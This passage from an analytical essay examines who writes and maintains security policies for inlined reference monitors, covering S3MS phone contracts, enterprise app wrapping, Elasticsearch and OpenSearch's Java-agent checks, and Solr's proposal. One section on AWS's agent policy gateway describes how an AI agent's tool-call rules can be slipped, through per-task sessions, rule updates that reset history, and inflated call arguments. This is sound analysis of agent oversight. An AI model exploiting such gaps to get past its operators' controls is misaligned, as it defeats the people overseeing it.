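The last column is partly guesswork, since few people record whom they blamed.

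Control-flow integrity fits the argument well because Microsoft and Google hold most of the roles for their own systems, while on Debian the compiler's developers, the packagers and each program's developers share them.

Every iPhone and Android app runs under a permission system, even though three parties share the writing of the policy and the user gets most of the benefit. Apple and Google could impose such a system because they control the phones, and developers had to accept the extra work to reach the phones' owners. The designers of SASI and Naccio had no such power. Divided roles therefore seem to hinder adoption mainly when no party can make the others cooperate.

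### What each candidate knows and lacks

*Security by Contract on the .NET Platform*, by Desmet, Joosen and colleagues, uses the example of a tourist who downloads a city guide to her phone. The guide needs the phone's navigation system and very little else. Four parties could write a policy for it.

The developer knows exactly what the guide does and why. *A Proof Carrying Code Framework for Inlined Reference Monitors in Java Bytecode* (2010) notes that a developer can also tune the inserted checks for speed in some places and code size in others. But a developer has little reason to restrict a program that already works, and a dishonest one would write a policy that permits the theft. Developers are better owners of the policy when they fear that attackers will hijack their software, as the makers of the search servers that adopted inlined monitors in 2025 and 2026 did.

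The tourist knows what she would object to, such as a large phone bill, but not what happens inside the guide. Phones of the time still asked users like her to decide whether to trust programs. Windows CE, Microsoft's system for small devices, asked whether to run any program without a recognised signature. Martinelli, Massacci and colleagues describe how Java phones asked the user to approve each sensitive action by a program from an unknown developer. Desmet and colleagues thought that the Windows question was too hard for users to answer and that most users lacked the skills to write policies.

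If the tourist's employer owns the phone, an administrator could write one policy for thousands of phones. The administrator knows which company data the phones hold and what the law requires, but usually has no source code. Without it, the administrator can't easily tell why a program requests network access and can't repair a program that a rule breaks.

The platform's maker knows every route to the network and can put checks beneath all of them. It can also update the checks whenever it adds a route, so nobody else has to maintain them. But it knows nothing about this particular guide or tourist, so its rules have to be general, and it may have other priorities. Dragoni, Massacci and Naliuka (2008), in *An Inline Monitoring System for .NET Mobile Devices*, considered changing the phone's virtual machine, but this would have required agreement from Microsoft or Sun. They expected that getting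 it would "dwarf any technical difficulty", and chose inlining instead.

### Security-by-contract

Dragoni and colleagues were working on S3MS (Security of Software and Services for Mobile Systems), a European research project that tried to give each party the part of the job it could do. In its scheme, security-by-contract, the developer ships the program with a contract that sets an upper limit on what the program will do, and the phone's owner sets a policy that limits what any program may do.

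*Provably correct inline monitoring for multithreaded Java-like programs* (Dam, Jacobs and colleagues, 2010) uses the example of a chess game for two phones. Each move takes 20 bytes over the internet or one text message, and the program stops after 100 moves. Its contract therefore states that the game will send no more than 2,000 bytes and 100 text messages. If the owner's policy allows 10,000 bytes and doesn't limit text messages, the game can run without a monitor.

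Let *B* be the set of event sequences that a program can actually produce, *C* the set its contract allows and *P* the set the policy allows. The program is safe to run unmonitored if

$$B \subseteq C \subseteq P.$$

The phone checks that *C* lies within *P*. Contracts and policies are both security automata written in ConSpec, which resembles PSLang. ConSpec is more limited, so that a computer can always determine whether every sequence allowed by one automaton is also allowed by the other.

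It is harder for a phone to check whether *B* lies within *C*, so the developer has to supply evidence, either a signature from a third party that has examined the program or a mathematical proof. An S3MS signature certifies that the program keeps to its contract, while an ordinary signature shows only where the program came from or that someone vouches for it in general. The phone's owner still decides whether the contract is acceptable. The phone can check a proof much more quickly than the developer can produce it.

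If the program has no contract, or its contract allows something that the policy forbids, the phone inserts a monitor. Suppose the phone's owner had set a limit of 1,000 bytes. The chess game's contract would no longer match, even though many games would stay under the limit. With a monitor inserted, a 40-move game would use 800 bytes and finish normally, but in a longer game the monitor would block the 51st move. Dragoni and colleagues explain that a program terminates if it doesn't handle the resulting error. The players would see the chess game crash and would probably complain to its developer, who had described the game correctly.

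Contracts are also easy to get slightly wrong. This is the part of the chess contract that limits text messages, with shortened names and explanatory comments:

```
int smsSent = 0;

BEFORE SmsMessage.Send()
PERFORM smsSent <= 100 ->       /* if so, allow the message */

AFTER SmsMessage.Send()
PERFORM true -> smsSent += 1;   /* then count it */
```

The count starts at zero and rises only after each message, so the contract allows 101 messages instead of the intended 100. This makes no difference under the example policy, but under a policy with a limit of 100, the contract would fail to match and the phone would insert a monitor into a game that never sends more than 100 messages.

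A developer can also insert the monitor before releasing the program. This suits old programs that nobody fully understands any more. Desmet and colleagues give the example of a policy that forbids all network access and limits a program to writing 1,000 bytes to disk. A certifier can easily see that a program contains no network code, so the developer needs to insert checks only for the disk limit. The developer can then test the result and fix anything the checks broke, which a phone's owner can't do.

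### What S3MS built and what became of it

The project built working prototypes. The .NET version ran on ordinary phones and accepted a program if it had a suitable signature or its contract matched the policy. It left inlining for last, because inlining works on any program but changes the code and slows it down. Dragoni and colleagues demonstrated inlining on two HTC phones playing chess by text message. On the monitored phone, the game terminated when it exceeded the user's limit. Martinelli and colleagues described a separate Java prototype that changed the runtime of a Linux phone instead of the program.

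Users in the demonstration picked one of four ready-made policies from a menu, ranging from unlimited connections to none, although the monitor could enforce any policy. Dragoni and colleagues suggested that phone operators might write such policies and offer them as a service, and Desmet and colleagues expected operators or large companies to write them.

Developers also had a reason to take part. *Nomadic devices, the freedom to compute* (2008) reports that phone operators were reluctant to accept software that had not gone through costly certification, and that the project hoped contracts would make approval cheaper. It also reports that France Telecom and Japan's DoCoMo were partners in the project, which had shown its prototype to companies in December 2007. The project's coordinator, Fabio Massacci, planned to trademark the name "security-by-contract" and look for investors.

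No operator is known to have deployed it. Costa, la Torre and colleagues later drew on the project's experience for another research monitor for mobile devices. In *A Survey of Runtime Policy Enforcement Techniques and Implementations* (2011), Gheorghe and Crispo analysed more than 100 papers and concluded that practical tools lagged behind the theory.

Besides the divided roles, changes in the phone market contributed to this outcome. The iPhone and Android soon displaced the Windows phones and Java phones that S3MS was built for. An Android developer lists the permissions an app needs, much as an S3MS developer would have written a contract. But Google decides which permissions exist, so nobody has to write an automaton, and Google's own software checks the permissions on every phone. Google took over the jobs that S3MS would have divided among operators, certifiers and developers.

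### Employers that wrap apps

Employers have a simpler arrangement available. In enterprise app wrapping, an employer rewrites an app to add its own rules before giving the app to staff. IBM's *About enterprise app wrapping* describes the process for one product:

1. An administrator uploads the app and chooses settings, such as sending all its traffic through the company's private network or encrypting the documents it downloads.
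2. The tool adds code that intercepts the app's calls to the operating system.
3. On the phone, the added code applies the administrator's settings to those calls.

App wrapping inlines a reference monitor, and the employer writes the policy, pays for it and benefits from it. Writing the policy takes little work because the administrator fills in a form. The form makes wrapping less flexible than Polymer, but it removes much of the difficulty of naming events, which the tool's vendor handles for all its customers.

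Divided ownership is not the only obstacle, since wrapping hasn't spread to most apps that employees use for work. Vendors restrict it mainly to apps that employers develop themselves or commission. IBM's tool doesn't accept apps from public app stores, and Microsoft has the same restriction for Intune, its system for managing work devices and apps. Omnissa, which sells a similar system called Workspace ONE, rules out store apps even when their developer supplies the file directly. The employer also needs credentials to sign the rewritten app, since wrapping invalidates the original signature.

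A second problem is who answers for faults in a wrapped app. Cisco gives customers copies of its Webex and Jabber apps for wrapping, but its *Mobile application management license agreement* states that Cisco doesn't test the wrapped versions and supports only the originals. A customer who finds a fault has to reproduce it in the unwrapped app before opening a support case. Cisco also expects customers to install each new version when it comes out, and warns that it may break the wrapping. An employer that wraps these apps therefore controls its policy but has to deal with faults in a program it can't repair. Microsoft advises customers to ask an app's developer about this in advance.

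Such faults are not rare exceptions, to judge by the vendors' own documentation. Ivanti's *Known wrapper limitations* lists dozens of features that wrapped Android apps can't use, including widgets, printing and Google Analytics. Some of the limits that vendors state are close relatives of the problems with SASI and Naccio:

| Vendor | Limit | Consequence |
|---|---|---|
| Omnissa | the tool can't interpret C and C++ libraries | an app may wrap successfully and then misbehave |
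| Omnissa | a ban on using the camera doesn't cover direct calls to the hardware on Android | an app can still take pictures by that route |
| Omnissa | the app's main code file must have room for the added methods | large apps may need restructuring |
| Omnissa | protection against tampering has to come off first | the app loses one defence to gain another |
| Ivanti | an app can't load Java code that the tool hasn't wrapped | the app wraps successfully but fails when it runs |
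| Ivanti | a new version of Android's build software renames an app's resource files | Ivanti advised developers to stay on the old version |

The camera gap is the same kind of mistake as naming only one of Java's methods for reading a file. But the vendor found and documented this gap, so administrators can at least know about it.

### From wrapping to building the controls in

Several vendors now favour giving app developers a software development kit (SDK) instead, a library containing the controls, which developers build into their apps. The employer still chooses the settings, but the developer, who knows the code, decides where the checks go.

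Microsoft's comparison of app wrapping and its SDK lists 37 controls, of which 30 work with either method and seven need the SDK. One of those seven is support for several identities, which lets an app hold a work account and a personal account and apply the employer's rules only to work data. A tool that rewrites finished code can intercept a save, but it can't easily determine which account the document belongs to. The developer can supply that information. Microsoft recommends the SDK for apps in public stores and apps that change often, and still recommends wrapping for internal apps whose source code the customer doesn't have.

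Citrix went further and ended its wrapping product, the MDX Toolkit. It planned to do this in September 2021 (Citrix, 2020), then in March 2022 (Citrix, *Migrating to the MAM SDK has never been easier*, 2021), and finally did so on 31 July 2023 (Citrix, *About the legacy MDX Toolkit*). The delays suggest that some customers still depended on the toolkit.

Citrix gave mostly technical reasons. An app that includes only the controls it needs is smaller and more robust. Phones had also begun to provide some of the controls themselves. Citrix's *How to get ready for the new MAM SDKs* (2020) explains that apps can rely on the phone's own encryption, which improves speed, stability and battery life because the phone no longer encrypts the same data twice. The platform was competing with Citrix's controls, much as operating-system sandboxes competed with inlined monitors.

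The change took some control away from employers. A Citrix customer used to be able to wrap an app supplied by another company, but now has to ask that company for a version with the SDK. If the company declines, Citrix suggests sending the app's traffic through a private network connection. The connection protects data on its way to the office, but it doesn't stop an employee from copying text out of the app.

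Wrapping therefore supports the argument about ownership only in part. Employers that held three of the four roles did adopt inlined monitors, whereas Naccio and Polymer never attracted many users. But wrapping worked best where the employer also controlled the app's code, so owning the policy was not enough without some influence over the program.

### Five parties that can restrict an agent

An AI agent has more possible policy writers than a phone app. Suppose that an online shop uses an agent to handle refunds:

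| Party | A rule it can set | What it doesn't know |
|---|---|---|
| model developer | train the model to refuse obvious fraud | the shop's refund terms |
| agent vendor | require approval before any payment | which payments are routine for this shop |
| tool provider | reject a refund larger than the original payment | why the agent wants to issue it |
| employer (the shop) | allow no refund of $500 or more | how the model will behave after its next update |
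| user (a member of staff) | approve or reject one refund | what other employees' agents have done |

A refund goes through only if all five sets of rules allow it, so wrongly blocked calls add up. As an illustration, suppose that each party's rules block 2% of legitimate refunds, independently of the others. The share that gets through is

$$0.98^5 \approx 0.90.$$

About one legitimate refund in ten fails, although each party would consider its own rules quite accurate. The shop gets the complaints about all the failed refunds but can change only its own rules.

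Even so, the shop is better placed to own its policy than anyone was to own a research monitor's. It knows its refund terms, loses money when the agent breaks them and hears from customers when the agent wrongly refuses. If it built the agent itself, it can also change the program when a rule causes trouble. A shop that buys a finished agent is more like an employer that wraps someone else's app. But the makers of agents such as Claude Code provide a place for customers' rules, whereas Cisco leaves customers to make wrapping work. A blocked tool call also usually gives the agent an explanation it can act on, so a bad rule is less likely to crash the program.

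### How Amazon's policy gateway divides the work

Amazon Web Services (AWS), Amazon's cloud business, sells an agent policy layer called Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore. AWS's *Why Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore chose Cedar for securing agentic workflows* explains how it works. A gateway between the agent and its tools compares each tool call with rules in Cedar, AWS's policy language, and blocks any call that no rule permits. This rule permits refunds below $500:

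```
permit (principal, action == AgentCore::Action::"ProcessRefund", resource)
when { context.input.refundAmount < 500 };
```

AWS placed the rules outside the agent and the tools because checks scattered through many programs are hard to audit. This also lets a security team change a rule without asking developers to change the agent. SASI had earlier offered a similar separation between policy and program.

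AWS is less definite about who should write the rules. *Amazon Bedrock AgentCore now includes Policy (preview), Evaluations (preview) and more* (2025) mentions development, compliance and security teams. *Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore is now generally available* (2026) says security, compliance and operations teams define the rules. In the developer guide, *Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore*, developers write them and security and compliance teams audit the results. A supplier wants its product to suit every kind of customer, so these descriptions are poor evidence of who writes the rules in practice.

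The product's permissions let a company divide the work. AWS's *AgentCore Gateway and Policy in AgentCore IAM Permissions* describes separate permissions for writing rules for particular gateways and for all gateways. A product team could have the narrower permission and a central security team the broader one. In Cedar a ban always overrides a permit, so the product team can't undo a central ban. However, the two permissions mainly determine how broad a rule someone can write, so the company needs other limits to keep one product team from writing rules for another's gateway.

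When several people write rules, the rules can contradict each other. In an example from AWS, one rule permits refunds under $100 for gold customers, and another bans refunds under $500 for gold and platinum customers. Each rule looks reasonable alone, but together they block every refund to a gold customer. Cedar's analysis tool can prove this from the text of the rules, and AWS rejects the change and describes the problem. Someone at the company still has to decide which team's rule should take priority.

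Authors can also test a rule before it affects anyone by using log-only mode, in which AWS records what the rule would have decided without enforcing it. New rules take effect at once unless the author chooses this mode. The gateway also needs permission to check the rules, and without it the gateway denies every tool call, even those the rules permit. A missing permission can go unnoticed in log-only mode and cause failures only once the company starts enforcing the rules. The rule's author would then get complaints about a mistake in someone else's configuration.

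Some rules also depend on facts that their author doesn't control. In AWS's example of a rule that gives a discount on large orders, the customer's status comes from a login token, which the model can't alter. But the number of items and the types of product come from the model's own tool call. If the call lists 50 items for an order of five, the rule permits the discount, and only the tool can compare that number with the real order. A shop that relies on such a rule therefore needs the tool's provider to do part of the checking.

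### Rules that depend on the agent's developer

Cedar evaluates each call separately, so it can't enforce SASI's example policy, "no messages sent after reading a file". In the summer of 2026 AWS released Dogwood, an extension of Cedar whose rules can refer to earlier tool calls. A Dogwood rule could block a message if the agent had read a file within the past day, the longest period AWS allows.

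Writing such rules takes knowledge that few compliance officers have. InfoQ's *AWS Open-Sources Dogwood, Extending Cedar to Govern Sequences of Agent Tool Calls* (2026) reports AWS's example of a $5,000 limit on an agent's transfers. If the agent requests three transfers of $2,000 at the same moment, a rule that adds up completed transfers permits all three, because the total is still zero. A rule that adds up requested transfers differs by only one word and blocks the third. Cedar's analysis tool can't catch the mistake because it doesn't work on rules about earlier events.

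The history also depends on the agent's developer. AWS's *Temporal policies* explains that AWS keeps a separate history for each session and that the calling software has to supply the session's identifier. If a developer's code starts a new session for every task, the agent can read a file in one session and send a message in the next. The message would go out even though the security team's rule was correct and the gateway enforced it. AWS warns that limits on how often an agent may act have the same problem.

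Changing a rule has a similar effect. When someone adds or updates a rule about earlier events, AWS ends the sessions that are open under such rules. The next call in each session fails, and the agent has to start a new session with an empty history. An agent that read a confidential file before the update can therefore send a message after it. To prevent this, the security team would have to tell the agent's developers about each change, and the developers would have to keep agents from carrying confidential data into their new sessions.

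## Search servers that adopted inlined monitors in 2025 and 2026

The makers of Elasticsearch and OpenSearch, two widely used search servers written in Java, each shipped an inlined monitor in 2025 that runs by default. These are the strongest counterexamples to the view that such monitors don't reach production. Each server's makers write its policies, maintain them and take the blame when the checks break something. They hold nearly all the roles that are divided among several parties for other monitors. Developers of a third search server, Solr, wrote an inlined monitor in 2026.

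Elasticsearch, OpenSearch and Solr had all relied on the Java Security Manager. Elastic's *Scripting and the Java Security Manager* explains that Elasticsearch ran it by default, with a policy meant to give each class only the permissions it needed. OpenSearch began as a copy of Elasticsearch's code and inherited this setup. Solr's developers added the Security Manager later to limit the damage an attacker could do by running arbitrary code on a server, and Apache Solr's *SOLR 13984* cites Elasticsearch as the example to follow.

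Java 24 then disabled the Security Manager, which hardly anyone else used. Elastic switched permanently to its own system, Entitlements, to keep a similar level of protection. OpenSearch replaced the Security Manager with a Java agent in version 3.0. Kumar and Perkins (2025), two Amazon engineers who worked on the replacement, write that they also explored the Linux service manager systemd and the alternative Java runtime GraalVM.

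### How the checks get into Java's library

A Java agent has nothing to do with AI agents. It is a component that can change other classes in a Java virtual machine, including those of Java's own library. Elasticsearch uses one in five steps:

1. *Attach.* Early in start-up, Elasticsearch connects to its own process and loads the Java agent into it.
2. *Configure.* The Java agent sets up the policies and an object that can check calls against them.
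3. *Insert.* It adds a call to that object inside each security-sensitive method of Java's library.
4. *Identify.* When a program calls one of these methods, the inserted code finds the class that made the call.
5. *Decide.* The checking object looks up what the policy grants to that class's module, and raises an error if the grant is missing.

Elastic's *All Classes and Interfaces* documents the order of the second and third steps. David Turner, an Elasticsearch developer, explains in *EntitlementBootstrap failure preventing startup* that only a Java agent can do the job, because the checks have to go into the running copy of Java itself. In simplified form, Java's method for opening a network connection then looks like this:

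```
void connect(SocketAddress endpoint) {
    InstrumentationRegistryHandle.instance().check$(
        "Socket.connect", Util.getCallerClass(), this, endpoint);
    /* the original code of connect */
}
```

Java's library can't normally access an application's classes, so Elastic keeps the few classes that the inserted code needs in a separate bridge package. Elastic's *Index* of that package explains that Elastic has its own `getCallerClass` because Java's method of the same name can fail when native code makes the call. There is then no calling Java class to report.

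A log in the forum thread *Elasticsearch WARN message after upgrade 8.19.2 to 8.19.3* records a refusal. The caller was Dynatrace, a commercial tool that monitors performance from inside a Java program. Shortened, with the oldest call first and explanations on the right, the log reads:

```
UrlUtils.createRestrictedURL     Dynatrace's code
java.net.URL                     Java's library creates a web address
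check$java_net_URL$              the inserted check
checkChangeNetworkHandling       classifies the action
neverEntitled                    no entitlement can permit it
notEntitled                      raises the error
```

The plugin's own code is unchanged. This is still inlining, because a separate tool inserts the checks into library code that the plugin calls, and the checks run in the plugin's process. Polymer worked the same way, and SASI's designers had reproduced the Security Manager with inserted checks in 1999. Changing the library also avoids some old problems. A call reaches the check whatever class name the plugin uses for it, plugins that load later need no rewriting, and their signatures stay valid.

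OpenSearch loads its Java agent through a start-up option. The agent walks the whole call stack and collects the JAR files (Java's packages of compiled code) that the methods came from, ignoring Java's own JARs. Every remaining JAR must have the required permission, as under the Security Manager. Elasticsearch checks only the calling class, so an application no longer needs all the permissions of its libraries. But Elasticsearch loses stack inspection's defence against luring attacks, in which code without a permission calls code that has it.

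### Seven entitlements and an old grammar

Elastic's *Entitlements* lists everything that a plugin's developer can request:

| Entitlement | What it permits |
|---|---|
| `manage_threads` | starting threads and changing their settings |
| `outbound_network` | connecting to other machines |
| `inbound_network` (deprecated) | accepting connections |
| `set_https_connection_properties` | changing an established HTTPS connection |
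| `load_native_libraries` | loading compiled code written outside Java |
| `files` | reading or writing the paths that the policy lists |
| `write_system_properties` | changing the global settings that the policy lists |

A policy can be very short. This is the complete file for a text-analysis plugin described in *Stable analysis plugin with native library fails entitlements in Elasticsearch 8.19.12*:

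```
ALL-UNNAMED:
  - load_native_libraries
```

The first line applies the grant to code outside named Java modules. During installation, Elasticsearch warned that the plugin requested an additional entitlement. The plugin still failed, although its user had confirmed that the source, the package and the installed copy all contained the right two lines.

According to Elastic's *Creating classic plugins*, each entitlement stands for a defined set of Java methods, and Elastic maintains that list. The plugin's developer therefore doesn't need to know which methods open a connection or load a library. Naccio's platform interface divided the work in much the same way.

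Keeping the list short makes entitlements less precise. `outbound_network` doesn't name a host, so a plugin that needs one server can contact any. Elastic warns that native code can bypass the file and network checks, so the two-line policy above grants nearly full access. Entitlements also keep no history, so they can't express SASI's rule "no messages sent after reading a file". Every plugin can read Elasticsearch's configuration directory, apart from files reserved for the server's core, so one with `outbound_network` could send much of that directory anywhere.

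Entitlements falls somewhere between a fixed-policy monitor and a configurable one. Plugin developers write policies, but only for events that Elastic has defined.

OpenSearch kept the Security Manager's policy language. Java was going to drop its own parser for policy files, so Kumar wrote a replacement. *Add a policy parser for Java Agent* (kumargu, 2025) says that the grammar stays the same to avoid breaking existing plugins. The new parser leaves out rules based on users, keys and signatures, which OpenSearch didn't need.

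Some policies stopped working even though the grammar stayed the same. OpenSearch's k-NN plugin, which finds similar items by comparing lists of numbers, reads the Linux file `/proc/cpuinfo` to find out what the processor can do. In April 2025 the Java agent began blocking this read. The call stack contained code from four JARs (the plugin, two parts of OpenSearch, and the search library Lucene), and Lucene's JAR had no permission to read the file.

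The plugin's request had worked under the Security Manager because it was inside a `doPrivileged` call, which stops the stack inspection from reaching older callers. The first version of the Java agent ignored `doPrivileged`. In *Limit stack walking in the java agent to frames before the call*, Perkins (as cwperks, 2025) traced a series of extra policy entries to this difference and proposed stopping at the `doPrivileged` call again. With the workaround in *Fix build due to phasing off SecurityManager usage* (reta, 2025), the plugin now checks the processor once, on a separate thread, while it loads. That thread's stack contains only the plugin and Java's own code, so Lucene's permissions don't matter.

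In the discussion of the stack change, Kumar warned against "writing our own security manager" piece by piece. OpenSearch already had its own policy parser by then. In May 2025, *Create equivalents of JSM's AccessController in the java agent* (cwperks, 2025) proposed also writing its own `doPrivileged`, because the Java agent relied on Java's version, which Java's developers planned to remove.

The Java agent also had the same kind of gap as SASI's example policy. In a test of two plugins that read the same file, cwperks found that the agent checked the one that used `FileChannel.open` but not the one that called `Files.readAllLines`, which internally opens the file through a different method.

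### Solr's proposal and the argument over it

Jan Høydahl, a Solr developer, began a discussion in May 2025 about what should replace the Security Manager. The first draft of the proposal, SIP-24, ruled out rebuilding it and suggested what Apache Solr called "low-hanging protection mechanisms". By the end of April 2026 the proposal was to adapt OpenSearch's Java agent, with four categories of protection:

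| Category | Methods that get a check | Default policy |
|---|---|---|
| files | those that read, write, copy, move or delete files | Solr's own directories |
| network | `Socket.connect`, `SocketChannel.connect` | the same machine, and any host on the ports that Solr and its coordination service use |
| shutdown | `System.exit`, `Runtime.halt` | callers on an approved list |
| other programs | `ProcessBuilder.start`, `Runtime.exec` | callers on an approved list, which starts empty |

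The network rule lists ports rather than hosts because servers join a Solr cluster over time, so a host list made at start-up would soon be incomplete. The rule has the same weakness as Polymer's rule for email ports, because any machine can listen on an allowed port.

By default, Solr's Java agent only logs and counts violations, as OpenShell does in its logging mode. It blocks them only if an operator sets `SOLR_SECURITY_AGENT_MODE=enforce`. Apache Solr planned to make enforcement the default in a later release.

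Under the proposal, Solr would not rely on the operating system alone for protection, because tools such as systemd and seccomp don't exist on Windows or macOS. David Smiley, another Solr developer, disputed this at the end of April, asking why the project should build and maintain protection that operators could get ready-made. He argued that anyone running Solr on a system without such tools could weigh the risk themselves. He saw the Security Manager as a secondary defence behind Solr's login and access controls, and he and his colleague Eric Pugh rejected the claim that going without a replacement was unacceptable. Smiley later clarified that he wasn't against doing something, but might give a mild "no" to anything that added too little security for the maintenance it needed.

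Høydahl answered that the Security Manager's file controls had protected Solr from many publicly reported vulnerabilities while the Security Manager was on by default. He said one central check would also be easier to maintain than separate checks at more than a hundred places in Solr's code. He doubted that many small or medium-sized organisations add operating-system limits themselves. He added that the project could remove the Java agent if maintaining it took more work than dealing with the flaws it prevented.

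Smiley's argument is strongest for files and connections, because Solr's default rules for these mostly apply to the whole process and a container can impose similar ones. Operating-system limits help less with shutdowns, since they can't easily distinguish a plugin that calls `System.exit` from a normal stop. Høydahl's doubt about operators fits Alhindi and Hallett's finding that few programs use sandboxes directly, although many companies run servers in containers. A container with default settings usually still allows outgoing connections, so its operator would have to add the network rule. Høydahl didn't list the vulnerabilities that the Security Manager had contained, so its main benefit is hard to judge.

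On 11 May Høydahl planned to start two days later, and on 27 May he opened the finished change for review under his GitHub name (janhoy, 2026, *SOLR-17767*). Language models wrote all 5,454 lines it added, partly by adapting OpenSearch's code, and also reviewed them. Getting the code this quickly from language models weakens the objection that a monitor takes a lot of work to build, but someone still has to maintain it.

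Testing and review turned up several mistakes in those first days:

- A symbolic link inside a permitted directory could point to a file outside it, and the check followed the link's own path instead of its target's.
- After the repair, tests on Linux failed because the policy still contained unresolved paths, so the two sides of the comparison didn't match.
- Permissions to exit or start programs that applied to one module's code never took effect, because the Java agent compared the module's file location with class names.
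- Solr failed to start on some systems because the inserted code runs as part of a Java library class and can't call a helper method unless that method is public.

Each mistake is easy to fix once someone notices it. The third would have blocked legitimate work only in enforcing mode, so its consequences would have stayed hidden for a while under the warning-only default.

The policy also became looser during development. The proposal asked operators to permit external connections for modules that need them. In the finished change, as janhoy described it, a wildcard lets five such modules connect to outside servers. The wildcard saves their users a configuration step but gives each module more access than it needs, much as `AllPermission` did.

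Smiley's review on GitHub called the change "very complete and well thought-out", though he had mostly skimmed the agent's code. He doubted that running Solr's ordinary tests under the Java agent would justify maintaining a second policy. The argument seems to have ended in agreement that the work was good, but without a formal decision on whether Solr should take it on. The change was still open on 30 May 2026, and no vote or merge is known. It is a serious attempt at adoption, but Solr doesn't yet meet the conditions for production that Elasticsearch and OpenSearch do.

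### What users ran into

Monitoring tools have caused some of the clearest conflicts. Tools such as Datadog's also insert code into a running Java program to measure it, so two tools end up rewriting code in the same process. In *How to Configure Trust/Entitlements for Datadog APM Java Agent on Elasticsearch 9.X* (flyxp11), a user reported that Elasticsearch blocked Datadog's tool at start-up because the tool lacked the `outbound_network` entitlement. The user wanted to follow individual requests from the company's applications through Elasticsearch. Turner recommended Elastic's own monitoring and doubted that a general tool would produce useful information. Datadog then confirmed that it hadn't certified its tool for Entitlements, and the user settled for monitoring only the applications that send the requests.

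Neither supplying a policy nor switching off the checks worked for a user of Arthas, a diagnostic tool for Java programs, according to *ES 8.19.5 encountered a NotEntitledException when attach to the ES process*. Elastic's documentation had long told customers not to attach such tools, because they can make a server unstable, and entitlements brought that advice closer to a prohibition.

Elastic has also blocked its own software. In version 8.18.0, some companies' staff could no longer log in through LDAP, a standard way to check passwords against a central directory. Kressin, in *LDAP Authentication Broken in Elasticsearch 8.18.0*, explains that Elastic's policy had omitted the network entitlement for the library that contacts the directory. Kressin's company sells a competing login product, but the error message he reproduces names exactly that library and entitlement. Elastic offered an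 encoded policy patch that administrators could add to a start-up file. Decoded, it reads:

```
versions:
  - 8.18.0
  - 9.0.0
policy:
  unboundid.ldapsdk:
    - set_https_connection_properties
    - outbound_network
```

The specialists who defined the entitlements had left out a permission their own server needed, even though the list has only a few kinds of permission. The mistake was obvious as soon as someone tried to log in, and administrators could fix it without waiting for new code. New warnings kept appearing in 2026, for example after upgrades to version 9.3.3, although someone replying in the forum thread *X-pack-security warnings after upgrading to 9.3.3* considered them harmless.

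Loading the monitor can fail too. In *EntitlementBootstrap failure preventing startup*, Elasticsearch 8.19.4 couldn't attach to its own process when its logs were on a particular kind of Amazon network storage with unusual file ownership. The same set-up had worked in 8.18. After more than two weeks of tests, the participants still hadn't found the exact cause, partly because the file in the error message was on a different disk.

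OpenSearch users have met similar trouble. The author of *Granting permissions to third-party JAR in lib/* wanted to add a logging library that sends its records to an outside server. The library had to load before any plugin, so it couldn't use a plugin's policy file. Java's old command-line option for supplying a policy had no effect, which is what Oracle documents for Java 24. The user finally unpacked OpenSearch's main JAR, added this rule to the policy inside and packed it up again:

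```
grant codeBase "${codebase.logagent.jar}" {
    permission java.net.SocketPermission "*", "connect,resolve";
};
```

The build system has to repeat this for every new version. The asterisk also lets the library connect to any host, although it needs only one.

Elastic offers no way to turn Entitlements off. A user named eereiter had written a plugin in Clojure, a language that creates new Java classes while a program runs, and asked how to permit this or disable the checks. Elastic replied that neither was possible, which left reworking the plugin as the only option. Plugins from outside the company can't have the `create_class_loader` entitlement, because code that loads classes from anywhere could compromise the server.

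Evans and Twyman expected people to disable any safety system that got in their way. Elastic's refusal prevents that but leaves some customers without a tool they used before. Solr takes the opposite approach, with a setting that keeps the Java agent from loading. Forum threads can't show how common these problems are, since people whose servers work have little reason to post.

### Which obstacles were missing

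Most of the proposed causes of low adoption were absent or weaker in Elasticsearch and OpenSearch, but not all of them:

| Obstacle | In Elasticsearch and OpenSearch |
|---|---|
| writing a policy from nothing | absent, because both had policies from the Security Manager |
| finding every event | reduced to a few categories, but OpenSearch still missed a way to read files |
| changes in the platform | persisted, since each new version of Java can add methods or remove ones the monitor uses |
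| free checks in the runtime | absent from Java 24 onwards |
| operating-system sandboxes | persisted, but can't give two plugins in one process different permissions |
| divided ownership | mostly absent, except for plugins and monitoring tools from other companies |

The platform problem persisted, but it was milder than it would have been for SASI's users. Elastic ships a particular version of Java with its server, so its developers can update the checks before customers receive a new version of Java. Someone who bought a rewriter in 1999 to use on other companies' programs had no such control.

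The deadline also seems to have mattered. Java's developers marked the Security Manager for removal in 2021, but both projects shipped their replacements only in 2025, the year of Java 24. Without a replacement, the projects would have had to stay on old versions of Java or give up a protection their customers already had. Companies faced no comparable pressure when Naccio and Polymer appeared, because they lost nothing by ignoring those systems.

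We can't tell from these projects how much each condition contributed, because each had one owner, a small set of events, an existing policy and a deadline. The cases also aren't independent, since OpenSearch grew out of Elasticsearch, and Solr followed Elasticsearch in adopting the Security Manager and followed OpenSearch in replacing it. But some employers adopted app wrapping without a deadline, so a deadline can't be essential.

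Adoption here is also weak evidence of demand. Customers received the monitor with an upgrade, and Elastic's customers couldn't decline it. The two servers show that a monitor with written policies can be technically fit for production, but they don't show whether many people would choose one if the software maker left the choice to them.
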